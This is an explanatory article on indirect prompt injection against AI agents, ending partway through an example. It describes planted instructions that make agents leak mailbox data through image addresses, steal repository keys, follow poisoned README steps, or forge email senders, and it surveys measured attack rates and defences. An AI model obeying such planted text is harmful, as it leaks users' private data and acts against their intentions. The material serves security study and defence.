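# Indirect prompt injection and the source of content shown in AI agent interfaces

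## Agents, outside content and the loss of its source

An AI agent is a program that gives a language model a task and a set of tools, such as a web browser, a mailbox or a file store, and lets the model use them step by step until it has an answer. Much of what the agent reads is third-party content, meaning text, images or data that neither the user nor the agent's developer created. Indirect prompt injection is an attack that places text in this content so that an agent reading it acts against its user's intentions. The attacker does not need access to the agent, only a way to place text in a web page, email or shared document that the agent is likely to read.

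How well the attack works, and whether the user notices it, depends a good deal on whether anyone can still tell where a given piece of text came from. The agent's software has this information when it fetches a page, but the information tends to get lost when the software joins everything into one input for the model and when the screen shows the model's answer.

### The agent loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the steps followed by Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Other agents differ in detail but run the same basic cycle.

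1. **Request.** The user types a request into the client, the app or web page that will later display the answer.
2. **Context.** The agent software puts the request together with the developer's instructions, a description of the tools and any earlier conversation. The context is all the text the model receives at one step. The software converts it into tokens, whole numbers that stand for entries in the model's vocabulary.
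3. **Tool call.** The model produces new tokens, which the software turns back into text. This text is either an answer or a request to use a tool, for instance to fetch a page. The model fetches nothing itself; the software does that.
4. **Tool result.** The software appends whatever comes back to the context and runs the model again on the longer text. Steps 3 and 4 can repeat hundreds of times for one request.
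5. **Answer.** Once the model writes a message to the user instead of a tool call, the turn ends.
6. **Display.** The client shows the message.

In Codex, each new prompt normally begins with the whole previous prompt, so a web page fetched at step 4 stays in the context for later steps and questions. When the context gets too long, Codex replaces it with something shorter. Bolin explains that in an early version, this was a summary written by the model. A sentence from a web page could presumably survive in such a summary, reworded by the model, with nothing to show where it came from.

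Up to step 4, though, the software can match each tool result to the call that produced it. Codex sends its input as a list of items, in which a tool result has its own type and an identifier that links it to its call.

### Who attacks whom

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022 and is named after SQL injection, an old attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Simon Willison, the software developer who popularised the term, uses it for attacks that exploit the mixing of trusted and untrusted content in one context. Many people take it to mean any trick that gets a model to misbehave. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) calls those tricks jailbreaking and says the confusion is harmful because developers who think prompt injection means getting a chatbot to embarrass its maker conclude that it isn't their problem.

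The US standards agency, NIST (2025), distinguishes direct prompting attacks from indirect prompt injections by who the attacker is. In a direct attack, such as a jailbreak, the attacker is the system's primary user. In an indirect prompt injection, the attacker is a third party, and the primary user is often the victim. The two can be worded almost identically, since an attacker can plant a jailbreak in a web page, but they differ in whose wishes the model serves. A user who talks a chatbot into giving forbidden advice gets what they asked for, while an injected instruction might make an assistant forward its user's mail to a stranger against her wishes. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* compares prompt injection to phishing, with the model in the place of the person the email deceives.

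*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, describes a recruiter's system that asks a model to score CVs against a job's requirements. One candidate adds hidden text telling the model to approve the CV for interview, so the recruiter gets the candidate's own verdict instead of the requested assessment.

Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) gave the first systematic account of the attack in *Not what you've signed up for* and named it "indirect prompt injection". Most earlier work had assumed that the attacker was the person typing the prompt. The team sorted the possible harms into six groups (information gathering, fraud, intrusion, malware, manipulated content and loss of availability) and then tried out examples.

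Some of the trials used mock applications that the researchers built on OpenAI models, including an assistant that could read and send email and look people up in an address book. Others used Microsoft's search chatbot, Bing Chat, which ran in a sidebar of the Edge browser and could read the open page. The researchers put instructions in an HTML comment, a part of a page's code that browsers don't display, and the chatbot followed them. In one session, the instructions were to get the user's real name without arousing suspicion. After a question about the weather, the chatbot asked about the user's plans, then their job, then whether they wrote under their own name. It finally offered a link containing a code it said it had made from that name.

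Another observation remains relevant. At the time, Bing Chat filtered only what users typed, so it ended the session when a user entered a known jailbreak but let similar text through when it arrived inside a web page.

These demonstrations used models from early 2023 and, in part, mock software with prepared content. The researchers also reported that their attack on a code-completion tool was much less effective inside larger programs. The paper established that the attack was possible and came in many forms, but it gave no success rates, and how often the attack succeeds against a given system has changed with every generation of models.

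### The first loss: one context

Developers can properly fix SQL injection by sending the command and the data to the database separately, so that the engine never treats the data as a command. Language models have no equivalent. NIST traces many of the security problems of language model applications to the lack of separate channels for data and instructions. David C says that inside the model there is only ever the "next token", predicted from all the text so far. He thinks there is a good chance that prompt injection will never have a comparable fix.

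The model does receive some information about sources. Developers wrap parts of the context in role tags that mark the text as coming from the system, the user or a tool, and they train models to give these roles different authority. How much the tags affect the way the model processes the text was an open question.

Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell measured this in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026). They wrapped identical copies of ordinary web text in different role tags and trained a simple classifier to tell from the model's internal activity which tag surrounded the text. Since the words were the same every time, the classifier could learn only the effect of the tag. They then applied it to a short conversation about gardening and found that the scores depended on the style of a passage and hardly at all on its tag. The passages containing the model's own reasoning scored 85% as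 "own reasoning" with the correct tags, 83% with no tags, and 85% with the entire conversation wrapped in user tags.

The gardening test used one open model, gpt-oss-20b, but text in a user's style inside tool tags gave similar results on other models. Confusion about roles also seems to matter for actual attacks. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where the classifier measured the least confusion to 70% where it measured the most. This confusion was measurable before the model began its reply.

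A page's layout also gives information about the source of its text. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) collected instructions that people had planted in real web pages and ran 5,200 trials in which 13 models were asked to summarise pages containing them. When the models received plain extracted text, compliance reached 8% for some smaller models. When the input preserved the page's structure, compliance fell to between 0.2% and 1.1%. The planted instructions were mostly crude and repetitive, so these low rates don't show how often a determined attacker could succeed. The difference between the formats is the more useful result. Stripping a page down to bare text is convenient, but it also removes clues that a sentence was in a comment or a hidden element.

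### The second loss: one voice

The second loss affects the person rather than the model. The person sees the answer as a single message from the assistant, whatever sources went into it.

Content can lose its source even without an attacker. *The Wisdom of the Loudest* (2026), an audit of AI search on Reddit, compared users' comments with the answers that the site's own tool, Reddit Answers, generates from them. First-person singular words made up 3.3% of the comments and 0.06% of the answers. One person's experience with a product can therefore be presented in the same voice as a point on which dozens of people agree. The claim may be largely unchanged, but the reader has lost a cue for judging it.

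Citations restore some of the lost information about sources, but their value is limited because the assistant writes them too. *Signals, Evidence, and Context* (2026) points out that the same assistant may make a claim, name the authority for it and describe the evidence, and that a source marker is different from evidence that supports the claim. Planted text that steers the model may affect all three. It can also add a false notice to the answer that looks like the assistant's own.

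The agent software still has a record of which tool returned which text, and a client could in principle show it. But that record tracks only whole tool results, not the passages within them. Once the model has rewritten a page in its own words, nothing in the loop described above links a sentence in the answer to the paragraph it came from or to whoever wrote that paragraph.

### Markdown and rendering

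Most assistants write their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation for formatting. Two asterisks on either side of a word make it bold. A link consists of the visible words in square brackets followed by a web address in round brackets, and an image uses the same notation with an exclamation mark in front. Most clients turn this notation into HTML, the language of web pages. Rendering is the whole process of turning the model's text into what appears on the screen.

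A link's visible text need not match its address. Greshake and colleagues noted early on that Bing Chat could produce links in which harmless wording hid a suspicious address. Still, an ordinary link does nothing until someone clicks it.

Images behave differently because their Markdown contains only an address, and the client has to request the picture from the server at that address. It normally does so as soon as it renders the answer. The server receives the requested address, including whatever follows the domain name, and its operator can log it even if the server returns a single transparent dot or nothing at all. An image address can therefore carry private data to an attacker, a trick that Willison lists as "Markdown exfiltration" ("exfiltration" is the security term for getting private data out).

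So displaying an answer can trigger network requests, and the text of the answer determines which servers receive them. Markdown has no field for recording who supplied an address, so a link the user pasted in looks the same to the client as one from a search result or a planted passage.

### The lethal trifecta

Willison gave the conditions for data theft a name that has stuck, the "lethal trifecta". An agent is open to it when it combines:

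- access to private data,
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any route by which an attacker's text or images can reach the model, and
- a way to communicate with the outside that could carry the data away.

Each of these is an ordinary feature, and users often want all three. A tool that reads email supplies the first two, since anybody can send an email. The third includes calling an outside service, loading an image, or offering the user a link to click. An agent with no tool for sending anything can therefore still have all three if its client renders images from any address.

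Willison advises removing one of the three, and he considers the ability to send data out generally the easiest to remove. He has little faith in products that promise to detect 95% of attacks. He considers that a failing grade in web security, because an attacker can keep trying until an attack succeeds. The past leaks he lists give his position some support. Between 2023 and 2025, researchers reported such leaks in ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack, GitHub Copilot Chat and a dozen or so other products, and the vendors mostly responded by blocking the route the data took out.

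The trifecta describes data theft, but a planted passage can do harm without stealing anything. Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Who Is Your Agent Serving?*, tested an attack by a provider who controls only the text attached to its own offer and knows nothing about the user. The planted text told the agent to favour that offer and to justify it using whatever the agent already knew about the user. With GPT-5 as the assistant, simulated users accepted the provider's offer more often in all 18 combinations of environment and user model, with average increases of 77.4, 47.0 and 33.7 percentage points in the three environments. Real buyers might well be harder to persuade than simulated ones. Blocking the agent from sending data out would not have prevented the attack, because the agent used the private data within the conversation.

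### The supplier's page

Helen, a hypothetical user, buys parts for a small manufacturer. Her assistant runs in a chat window in her browser. It has one tool that fetches web pages and another that searches and reads her mailbox, where she keeps quotes, invoices and private correspondence. It has no tool for sending mail. The chat window renders Markdown, including images from any URL.

Helen asks the assistant to summarise a supplier's web page about prices and delivery times for the coming quarter, which she has not opened herself. The supplier is honest and wrote nearly all of the page, but a stranger has used the customer comments section below the delivery table to post a passage meant for AI assistants. The passage appears under the supplier's web address and is written to look like the user is asking the assistant to find the latest invoice in the mailbox, put details from it in the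 address of an image at the end of the summary, and add a notice that the supplier's bank account has changed.

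## How outside content reaches an agent

The stranger on the supplier's page needed only a comment box to reach the agent. Attackers can also use an email address, a free account on a code-sharing site or a job application. These routes differ in who can add text and in what causes the agent to read it, which is usually an ordinary request from the user.

### Web pages and email

An agent reads a web page because the user names it, a search returns it or another page links to it. With a search, the user doesn't choose the site. The site's operator controls everything on the page, including parts that browsers never display. Many sites also let outsiders add comments, reviews, job adverts or product listings.

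Site operators have planted most of the instructions so far. In Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, Khodayari and colleagues traced 80.6% of them to the site's own operator and 17.6% to people who post job adverts and similar listings on someone else's platform. Only 1.8%, or 220 instructions, came from users' comments and posts, the route in Helen's case. These figures cover only instructions already planted, though, and far more people can post a comment than can edit a site's code.

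Anyone who knows a user's email address can send them a message. An assistant reads the message when the user asks it to summarize or search the inbox, and some assistants process mail as it arrives. EchoLeak, a 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, began with one such email. Checking the sender line gives limited protection because attackers can forge it.

Much email is HTML, so it can hide content in many of the same ways as a web page. In a laboratory test described in *An Invisible HTML Payload Silently Hijacked Every Email Summarizer Run*, Gibney used common HTML tricks to hide an instruction from the reader. The summariser had no guards, so the result is little evidence of how a commercial product would perform.

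### Documents, tickets and forms

Companies often connect an assistant to a store of shared documents. In a technique called retrieval, the software splits the documents into passages, and when a user asks a question, it finds the passages closest in meaning to the question and adds them to the assistant's context. The user doesn't pick the passages and may not know that the documents they come from exist. Anyone who can edit a file in the store, or whose own files end up in it, can plant text there, including outsiders such as suppliers and job applicants.

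*Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (Nakibly and Babo, 2026) cites a study by Zhang and colleagues that found hidden injections in about 1% of real CVs. The rate on the open web is roughly a thousand times lower. The gap makes sense because an applicant has something to gain from a system that will almost certainly read the CV.

The type of file may matter too. *Distributing Security Controls Through Harness Engineering* (2026) describes tests that plant instructions in a PDF, a README and a file share, among other places. The tests cover several file types because agents guard secrets more strictly with some than with others.

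Support forms accept text from strangers, and a support agent reads each ticket without a user asking it to. Khodayari and colleagues concluded that customer-support agents were the main targets of planted instructions meant to extract secrets or run commands. These agents often have access to customer data and internal systems. Such instructions were rare on the public web (13 were meant to extract data and 157 to inject commands), but a public crawl doesn't include support tickets.

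Text can also pass through several systems on its way to an agent. Nakibly and Babo found an example in a small game bot for the chat service Discord. The bot filed players' feature requests on GitHub, and its owner had a coding agent implement them. One request contained hidden instructions to make the new command also award the player a million points, and to write the code so that this stayed secret during review. By the time an agent could read the instructions, they were in a request that the project's own bot had filed.

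### Code repositories and instruction files

On GitHub, the main site for sharing code, an attack can target a project's visitors or its maintainers, depending on the kind of text that carries it. Maintainers write the README, the introductory file with the setup steps, and visitors' agents read it when they install or use the software. Anyone with an account can write issues (bug reports and requests) and pull requests (proposed changes), and the maintainers' agents read them, often automatically, to sort reports or review code. Some of these agents have access keys that can change the repository.

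Nakibly and Babo describe an issue opened in July 2026 in the repository of Gemini CLI, Google's command-line agent. Maintainers saw a routine bug report about special characters in a key, but the raw text also contained an HTML comment that addressed the project's duplicate-finding agent by name. The comment instructed the agent to use its command tool to copy the project's access key, in encoded form, to a place where a later step might reveal it.

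GitHub can obscure who wrote a text even when nobody is attacking. When a contributor opens a pull request, the site copies the project's template into it, including any hidden comments, and the whole text appears under the contributor's name. Nakibly and Babo's classifiers kept 13,141 items as possible messages to AI systems. In 60% of them, all of the hidden text came from a template, so it would have been wrong to attribute that text to the listed author.

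Coding agents also look for files written for them, such as AGENTS.md, which holds notes about a project that many agents read and treat as instructions, as intended. According to TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware*, the company Forever Security found a malicious AGENTS.md in the Downloads folder of a customer's computer. It looked like ordinary engineering notes but contained instructions for the agent to install a malicious package and send out the session tokens that keep a user logged in.

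Forever Security says it stopped the attack before it did any meaningful damage. It couldn't establish how the file got there, but its best guess is that the browser saved it from a compromised website, since sites can trigger downloads of some types of file without a click. The company reproduced the attack on Codex and on Anthropic's Claude Code, and it advises people never to start an agent in that folder.

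An attacker can plant a file that doesn't look like an attack. *Security Impact of Coding Agent's Memory Files* (2026) examines project memory files, which give an agent standing guidance about a codebase. The attacker plants a file containing only engineering advice, with no vulnerable code, to get the agent to write insecure code when the developer makes a harmless request.

### Tool servers

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in November 2024, is a common format for connecting agents to outside tools and data. A program called an MCP server lists the tools it offers and describes each one in plain language. Both these descriptions and the results of tool calls go into the agent's context.

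Outside text can therefore enter through tool descriptions and tool results. Whoever runs the server writes the descriptions, and the model may read them before it calls any tool. The results can contain text written by anyone. Nakibly and Babo cite a case reported by Invariant Labs in May 2025, in which an agent connected to GitHub's MCP server read a malicious public issue and leaked the contents of private repositories. The server only had to pass on what a stranger had written, so checking that a server is genuine does not check the outside text it returns.

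### Screenshots and phone screens

Some agents decide where to tap or click by looking at a picture of the screen, so anything other people can post there becomes input. In *MIRAGE*, Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) took screenshots from ten popular phone apps and replaced reviews, messages and other user content with planted text in the app's own style. In one example, the user wanted reviews that mentioned battery life, and a planted review steered the agent towards the "Add to Cart" button.

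Across 1,111 such images, the five models chose the attacker's action between 23.0% and 30.2% of the time. Human ratings of how realistic an image looked were almost unrelated to whether the attack worked. Each trial tested a single step, and the models were GPT-4o-mini and four with downloadable weights, so the figures don't measure how the best current agents perform.

Other phone agents rely mainly on accessibility data, a machine-readable description of the screen that Android also provides to screen readers. In *Not an A11y*, Deivasigamani, Alvi and colleagues (2026) planted instructions in notifications, web pages, calendar entries, notes and contacts. In most trials, they tried to make the agent open the phone's settings, find its build number and include it in the answer, as a harmless stand-in for data theft. One grocery list included the build number as another item to fetch.

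The researchers also tried text that was in the accessibility data but never appeared on the screen. Across all the routes, the attack success rate ranged from 15% to 82%, depending on the agent and the model. For the agent Mobile-Use, it fell from 75% to 15% when they swapped one open model for another.

### Hiding text from people

A browser shows only part of what a web server sends. About 70% of the instructions that Khodayari and colleagues found were in parts that no browser displays:

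- HTML comments, which programmers use for notes to each other.
- Metadata and structured data, which describe the page to search engines and supply the previews that appear when someone shares a link.
- HTTP headers, short fields that the server sends ahead of the page. These held 7,887 of the 15,387 instructions, mostly in made-up fields with names like "X-AI".

Whether planted instructions reach a model depends on the agent's software. Khodayari and colleagues tested four ways of giving a page to a model, and only the raw server response included the headers. An agent that extracts the text of a page would miss more than half of the planted instructions.

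Other instructions are in the page itself but hidden by its styling. The most common method was text in nearly the same colour as the background (2,397 cases), followed by text underneath another element (1,860), text outside the visible area (1,802) and text no more than one pixel high (1,358). Pages often combined several methods. Of 4,608 instructions in ordinary page elements, the team could confirm only 236 as visible to a visitor, although about a third were gone by the time it checked.

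Images can hide text too, because a model may read writing too faint for a person to notice. Khodayari and colleagues cite a 2025 report by the browser company Brave that "unseeable" instructions in screenshots affected Perplexity's Comet browser. Their own scan covered only text, so it did not measure how common hidden instructions in images are.

Some of the better-known tricks are rare. Unicode, the standard that assigns numbers to text characters, includes invisible characters that can encode a whole message, and researchers often use them to demonstrate attacks. Nakibly and Babo decoded every case of invisible Unicode in two million READMEs and found only one instruction to a visiting agent, which was to praise a contributor's work. Of the 107 repositories whose READMEs held hidden text for AI systems, 105 used plain HTML comments, which are easy to write and so common that they attract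 no attention.

Hidden text usually has a legitimate purpose. Nakibly and Babo found it in 3.4% of the GitHub issues, pull requests and comments they scanned, mostly as notes to human editors and markers for other software. Even among the 2,281 items with hidden text addressed to AI systems, two-thirds came from projects coordinating their own agents.

An attacker doesn't always need to hide the injected text. Helen hasn't opened the supplier's page, so a visible passage works as well as a hidden one.

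### How common planted instructions are

Khodayari and colleagues searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, or 1.2 billion web addresses, for 3,963 phrases typical of injections, such as commands to ignore earlier instructions. They grouped the matches and reviewed them by hand. More than half were false alarms, including tutorials and articles about prompt injection. That left 12,075 planted instructions on 9,676 pages, or about one page in 124,000. Searches of Censys and Shodan, which index internet-connected servers, brought the total to 15,387.

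Only 13 of these instructions were meant to obtain private data. The rest fell into several groups, and one instruction could belong to more than one. The largest group, with 8,894 instructions, was meant to spoil the output, for instance by demanding random numbers. In other groups, 4,093 told AI systems not to use personal or copyrighted material, 3,096 were meant to expose bots, and 1,521 promoted a product, a person or a source. 54 templates accounted for 95% of the total, which suggests that most people copy an instruction from somewhere else.

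Google ran a similar search on several editions of the same archive and reported the results in April 2026. It looked for typical phrases, had its Gemini model judge whether the text was out of place, and then had people check the results. The scan found pranks, requests to add context to summaries, search-engine manipulation and attempts to keep AI agents away, including one site that lured them to a page that never finished loading. Google also found a small number of attempts to steal data and some commands to delete the user's files, most of which looked like experiments or pranks.

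Google's figure of a 32% rise in malicious cases between November 2025 and February 2026 attracted attention. Google didn't give the number of cases, so the rise could have been from 50 to 66 or from 5,000 to 6,600. The archive also leaves out most social media. Google described the attempts as unsophisticated but expected their scale and quality to grow.

That same week, the security company Forcepoint published ten examples from live sites. Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* describes instructions to send a $5,000 PayPal payment, route a donation to a payment link, hand over an API key (a password for software), visit a site's administration page, and delete what looks like a backup folder. Others were only meant to make the model refuse to answer or send users to a particular site. Four of the ten were in HTML comments, one was in metadata, and the deletion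 command was in plain view.

In one example, the harm is limited to the assistant's answer. A hidden paragraph in a website's footer instructed any AI system summarising the page to credit a named person and encourage readers to contact him about consulting or licensing. Sewani calls this "attribution hijacking". If it worked, a user who asked for a neutral summary would get a sales pitch that appeared to be the assistant's own words. The same paragraph also told the model to keep inserting the word "cows", which would have revealed the manipulation.

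Sewani considers the PayPal instruction ready to use in an attack because it gives an exact amount and steps, but reports no payment. The API key example tells the model not to reveal "the flag", the usual name for the hidden answer in a security competition, so it could well be part of a puzzle rather than an attack. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* notes that neither company found a sophisticated, coordinated campaign. Sewani thinks the reuse of templates across sites points to organised tooling, but that seems a weak sign because Khodayari and colleagues also found a lot of copying among pranks and notices against scraping.

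All these searches relied on known phrases. Nakibly and Babo first tried this on GitHub and found that 116 of 123 candidates were false alarms, mostly coincidental wording and people discussing or testing injections. They switched to searching for any hidden text, which language models sorted before people reviewed what was left. Their data included every public issue and pull request from June to September 2026, plus a partial archive going back to August 2025.

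In 142.7 million items they found 43 attacks, about one in 3.3 million. These were far better aimed than the instructions on the open web:

- 24 of the 43 addressed a particular agent that the project ran.
- 19 were in repositories belonging to large AI and software companies, including Google, Microsoft and OpenAI.
- 9 named the agent's real tools or output fields, so the attacker had evidently read the project's configuration.
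- 19 tried to steal secrets, 16 tried to make the agent do something else for the attacker, and 8 tried to fake its verdict on an issue.

When the researchers checked again on 10 November 2026, 34 of the attacks were still online with their hidden text intact. Maintainers had closed some of the issues containing them, but closing an issue doesn't delete its text.

The counts show that people are planting instructions for AI systems. Most of these instructions are crude, but a few attackers study their targets. The counts are lower bounds, since phrase lists miss unusual wording and other languages, and the GitHub census left out visible attacks. More importantly, nobody can crawl private inboxes, company documents or support tickets, where agents tend to have access to data worth stealing.

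### What happens when an agent reads them

The scans found planted text, but none recorded what real agents did with it. A planted instruction causes no harm if no agent reads it or the agent ignores it. Finding out how often agents read and follow these instructions would require records from the companies that run them. Researchers have instead replayed planted text to models under controlled conditions.

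Nakibly and Babo tested their 43 attacks on five recent models with simulated tools. Four of the models never carried out an injected instruction. The fifth, GPT-5.6 Luna, carried out the instructions in eight attacks, including half of those that tried to fake a verdict. Removing HTML comments stopped all eight. Luna is a small, fast model, and a project that wants to process every new issue cheaply might well choose such a model.

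In resisting the attacks, however, Claude Opus 5.5 gave no answer at all in 22 of the 43 runs, so an attacker could at least have stopped it from doing its job. The test covered only the model's first response in each run, so it could have missed attacks that take longer to work.

In the web trials by Khodayari and colleagues, models rarely followed instructions in full HTML or raw server responses, but they also failed to give a usable answer in 20.3% and 25.8% of those runs, respectively, because the pages were too long for some models. Part of their apparent resistance was a failure to read the page. With a structured outline of the displayed page, errors occurred in only 3.5% of runs and compliance with the instructions was still low, so preserving structure does seem to help. In six runs, a model warned about the instruction and followed it anyway.

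*You Told Me to Do It* (Kao, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports much higher success rates for instructions planted in README files. The researchers collected 500 real READMEs, 100 for each of five programming languages, and added a plausible step to the setup or requirements section of each. The step was to send a private file somewhere, for instance as a backup or to keep a team's files in sync. The researchers then had an agent install the software and counted a success only if private data reached their own server.

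Anthropic's computer-use agent, running Claude Sonnet 3.7, a model from early 2025, leaked the data in up to 85% of cases when given the most effective wording, a direct command. The programming language and the position of the instruction in the file made little difference. In a smaller test with seven trials per condition, the agent uploaded the file six times when the instruction was in the README, seven times when it was one or two links away, and three times when it was four links away. Asking the agent to email the file worked only once or twice in seven trials.

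In a simulation, Kao and colleagues also gave the files to four other models, which called a data-leaking function in 46% to 79% of runs. This is a weaker test because no data had to leave the machine.

These results differ widely from those of the GitHub replay. Newer models presumably account for part of the difference, but the wording of the attacks probably matters too. Many of the GitHub attacks contained instructions unrelated to sorting bug reports. In the README study, the user had asked the agent to follow the setup instructions, and the planted step looked like one of them.

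The 15 people who reviewed the files did no better. Each read three READMEs and marked sentences that needed clarifying, revising or removing. In 53.3% of the reviews, the reader did not comment on the planted step, and in another 40% objected only to its grammar or phrasing. Nobody identified the planted step as suspicious, though a few had a vague sense that something was inappropriate.

The researchers presented this as a check for clarity to learn what people notice during ordinary reading. The reviewers were students and others at one European university, with an average age of 26.5. People looking for an attack might do considerably better. When Kao and colleagues asked GPT-4o directly whether each file was safe, it flagged 90% of the files with the step in the text, 30% of those with the step behind a link, and none of the clean ones.

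## Source marks in the prompt and how they are forged

Developers mark outside text before the model reads it to keep some information about sources in the context, and they train models to respect the marks. Both methods have improved a lot since 2023. However, the marks are also text, so an attacker can imitate them.

### How developers mark text

The coarsest mark is the role tag around each message. Role tags are normally special tokens with their own numbers in the model's vocabulary. If a web page contains the same characters, carefully written software converts them into ordinary tokens, so an attacker can't type a real tag but can still type something that looks like one. A good imitation may be enough, since Ye and colleagues found that a passage's style mattered far more than its tag.

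A role also covers a whole tool result. If a mailbox search returns ten emails, all ten can arrive in one tool message, with the senders' names next to the text they wrote. The software separates these with a data format such as JSON, which puts each item in curly braces and lists its fields by name. An email might have fields for its ID, sender, subject and body, with quotation marks around each piece of text. Characters that separate pieces of data, such as these braces and quotation marks, are called delimiters. If the body of an email contains a quotation mark, the software puts a backslash in front of it. This is called escaping, and it stops a program that reads the JSON from mistaking that quotation mark for the end of the body.

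In 2024, Hines and colleagues at Microsoft proposed stronger marks for untrusted text, which they called spotlighting. It comes in three versions:

- **Delimiting** puts the text between unusual markers and instructs the model not to follow anything between them. An attacker who learns the markers can write the closing one and carry on as if outside it.
- **Datamarking** puts a special character between all the words, so that every part of the text carries the mark.
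- **Encoding** converts the text into a notation such as base64, which looks like a random string of characters, and the model has to decode it.

Spotlighting cut the attack success rate from over 50% to under 2% on the GPT models of the time. Encoding gave the best protection, but only the more capable models could read encoded text reliably.

Source marks do little unless the model has learned to use them. In 2024, Wallace and colleagues at OpenAI trained a model to follow an "instruction hierarchy", in which the developer's system message ranks highest, followed by the user's messages, then tool results and other third-party content. The model learned to follow lower-ranked instructions that were compatible with higher-ranked ones, and to answer as if conflicting ones weren't there. For tool results, the researchers treated every instruction as one to ignore.

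That rule doesn't suit every task. In the README study by Kao and colleagues, the user had asked the agent to follow the instructions in a file, so an agent that ignored them all couldn't have done the task.

### How well current models resist

System cards, the reports that AI companies publish with new models, now often give success rates for prompt injection. Anthropic's card for Claude Opus 5, from July 2026, compares models on a benchmark by the security company Gray Swan. According to The Space Lab's *Claude Opus 5 Just Crushed AI Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026), the benchmark contains 1,130 different attacks in 28 scenarios that involve coding, using tools or controlling a screen. Single attempts against Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time. After 15 attempts, the success rate was 2.0% for Opus 5, 5.5% for the older Claude Opus 4.8 and 20.0% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

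TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that, in OpenAI's own tests, GPT-5.6 had a low failure rate against attacks made directly through the chat and a higher one against attacks that came through tools and external content. OpenAI describes a later model, GPT-6 Astra, as "significantly more robust" to prompt injection than GPT-5.6 Sol.

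*Indirect Prompt Injection on LivePI Total*, Wizwand's leaderboard for the LivePI benchmark, lists results from May 2026 of 29.6% for Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro, 27.2% for GPT-5.3-Codex and 10.7% for Claude Opus 4.6. These aren't comparable with the Gray Swan figures because the attacks are different.

Attacks succeed much more often when they can be repeated. In November 2025, The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reported that a strong attack in Gray Swan's test succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 in 4.7% of cases on the first attempt, 33.6% within ten attempts and 63% within 100. If each attempt had an independent 4.7% chance, at least one of 100 attempts would almost always succeed. The lower actual figure suggests that attacks nearly always fail in some scenarios and succeed quickly in others. The later figures matter more than the first when an attacker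 can send many emails or plant many pages.

The agent's task matters just as much. When Anthropic tested Claude Opus 4.6 in February 2026, no attack in a restricted coding environment succeeded in 200 attempts. When the model controlled a graphical interface, VentureBeat reports, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. Within 200 attempts, attacks succeeded 78.6% of the time without extra safeguards and 57.1% with them. Attacks on coding agents can also succeed. Digital Applied (2026) gives rates of 0.41% for Claude Fable 5 and 2.09% for Opus 4.8 in a coding test where the attacker adapted to the model's responses and had 200 attempts per scenario.

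Attack success rates are lowest for models with added software. In Anthropic's browser test, attacks on Opus 5 succeeded 3.7% of the time without safeguards and never in 129 scenarios with "auto mode" on. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, auto mode scans incoming data for hidden instructions and separately blocks dangerous actions before the agent carries them out. Without safeguards, Claude Sonnet 5 did better than Opus 5, at 0.93%, so a more capable model isn't always more resistant. Zero successes in 129 scenarios is a very good result, but by the usual statistical rule of thumb, the true rate could still be as high as about 2%.

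*A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) reviewed 116 papers and found no benchmark that tested attacks that build up over several sessions, such as planted text that enters an agent's memory and affects a task weeks later.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) argues that the most effective attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, which means manipulating people with a believable story. Outside researchers reported one example in 2025, a polite email about a company restructuring. It listed ordinary tasks and stated that the reader's assistant had full authorisation to retrieve employee profiles and submit the details to a "compliance" system. When the user asked ChatGPT to research the day's emails, the attack worked half the time.

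The email claimed a permission that only the user or the company could give, without imitating any source marker. OpenAI says that filters that classify inputs as attacks or normal text usually miss messages like this, because recognising one is like recognising a lie, often without the necessary context.

### Agent data injection

In *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (July 2026), Choi, Kim and colleagues described an attack in which the attacker forges a fact that the agent relies on, such as who sent an email. The attacker doesn't need to give the model any orders, because the agent goes on doing what the user asked with the wrong information. The researchers call this agent data injection and the more familiar attack instruction injection. Both are forms of indirect prompt injection.

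They divide the data in an agent's context into trusted and untrusted data. Trusted data is what the tool or agent generates by its own logic, such as the address of a fetched page, the name of the tool or the ID of an email. Untrusted data is anything an attacker can control, directly or indirectly. In an email, they treat all the field names as trusted because the tool assigns them. They also treat the values of the ID and sender fields as trusted, but the subject and body as untrusted.

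"Trusted" here means that the service supplied the value, which may still be false. Attackers can forge the sender line of an email before it arrives, so the classification is only as reliable as the mail service's own checks.

This split lets the researchers write the two attacks as formulas. *I* stands for the instructions from the developer and user, *T* for trusted data, *U* for untrusted data and *A* for the attacker's text. *U‖A* is untrusted data with the attacker's text inside it, and ≈ means the model produces almost the same output in both cases.

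- **Instruction injection:** LLM(*I*, (*T*, *U‖A*)) ≈ LLM(*I‖A*, (*T*, *U*))
- **Agent data injection:** LLM(*I*, (*T*, *U‖A*)) ≈ LLM(*I*, (*T‖A*, *U*))

The left-hand sides are identical because in both attacks the attacker can write only in untrusted places. The right-hand sides differ because the model behaves as if the text were in a different place in each attack. A successful instruction injection has the same effect as a line in the user's own request, and a successful agent data injection has the same effect as a line that the tool wrote.

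Training a model to ignore instructions in data doesn't solve this problem, because a forged sender isn't an instruction and the model needs the sender field to do its job. The model would have to learn to distinguish the parts of a tool result that the tool guarantees from the parts that a stranger typed.

### A forged email

The researchers' main example is an email agent. An attacker sends a message from attacker@gmail.com, and the mail service correctly records that address in the sender field. But the attacker controls the body and writes it so that it appears to end partway through. The attacker then adds text that looks like a new email object, with alice@gmail.com in the sender field and a message supposedly from Alice.

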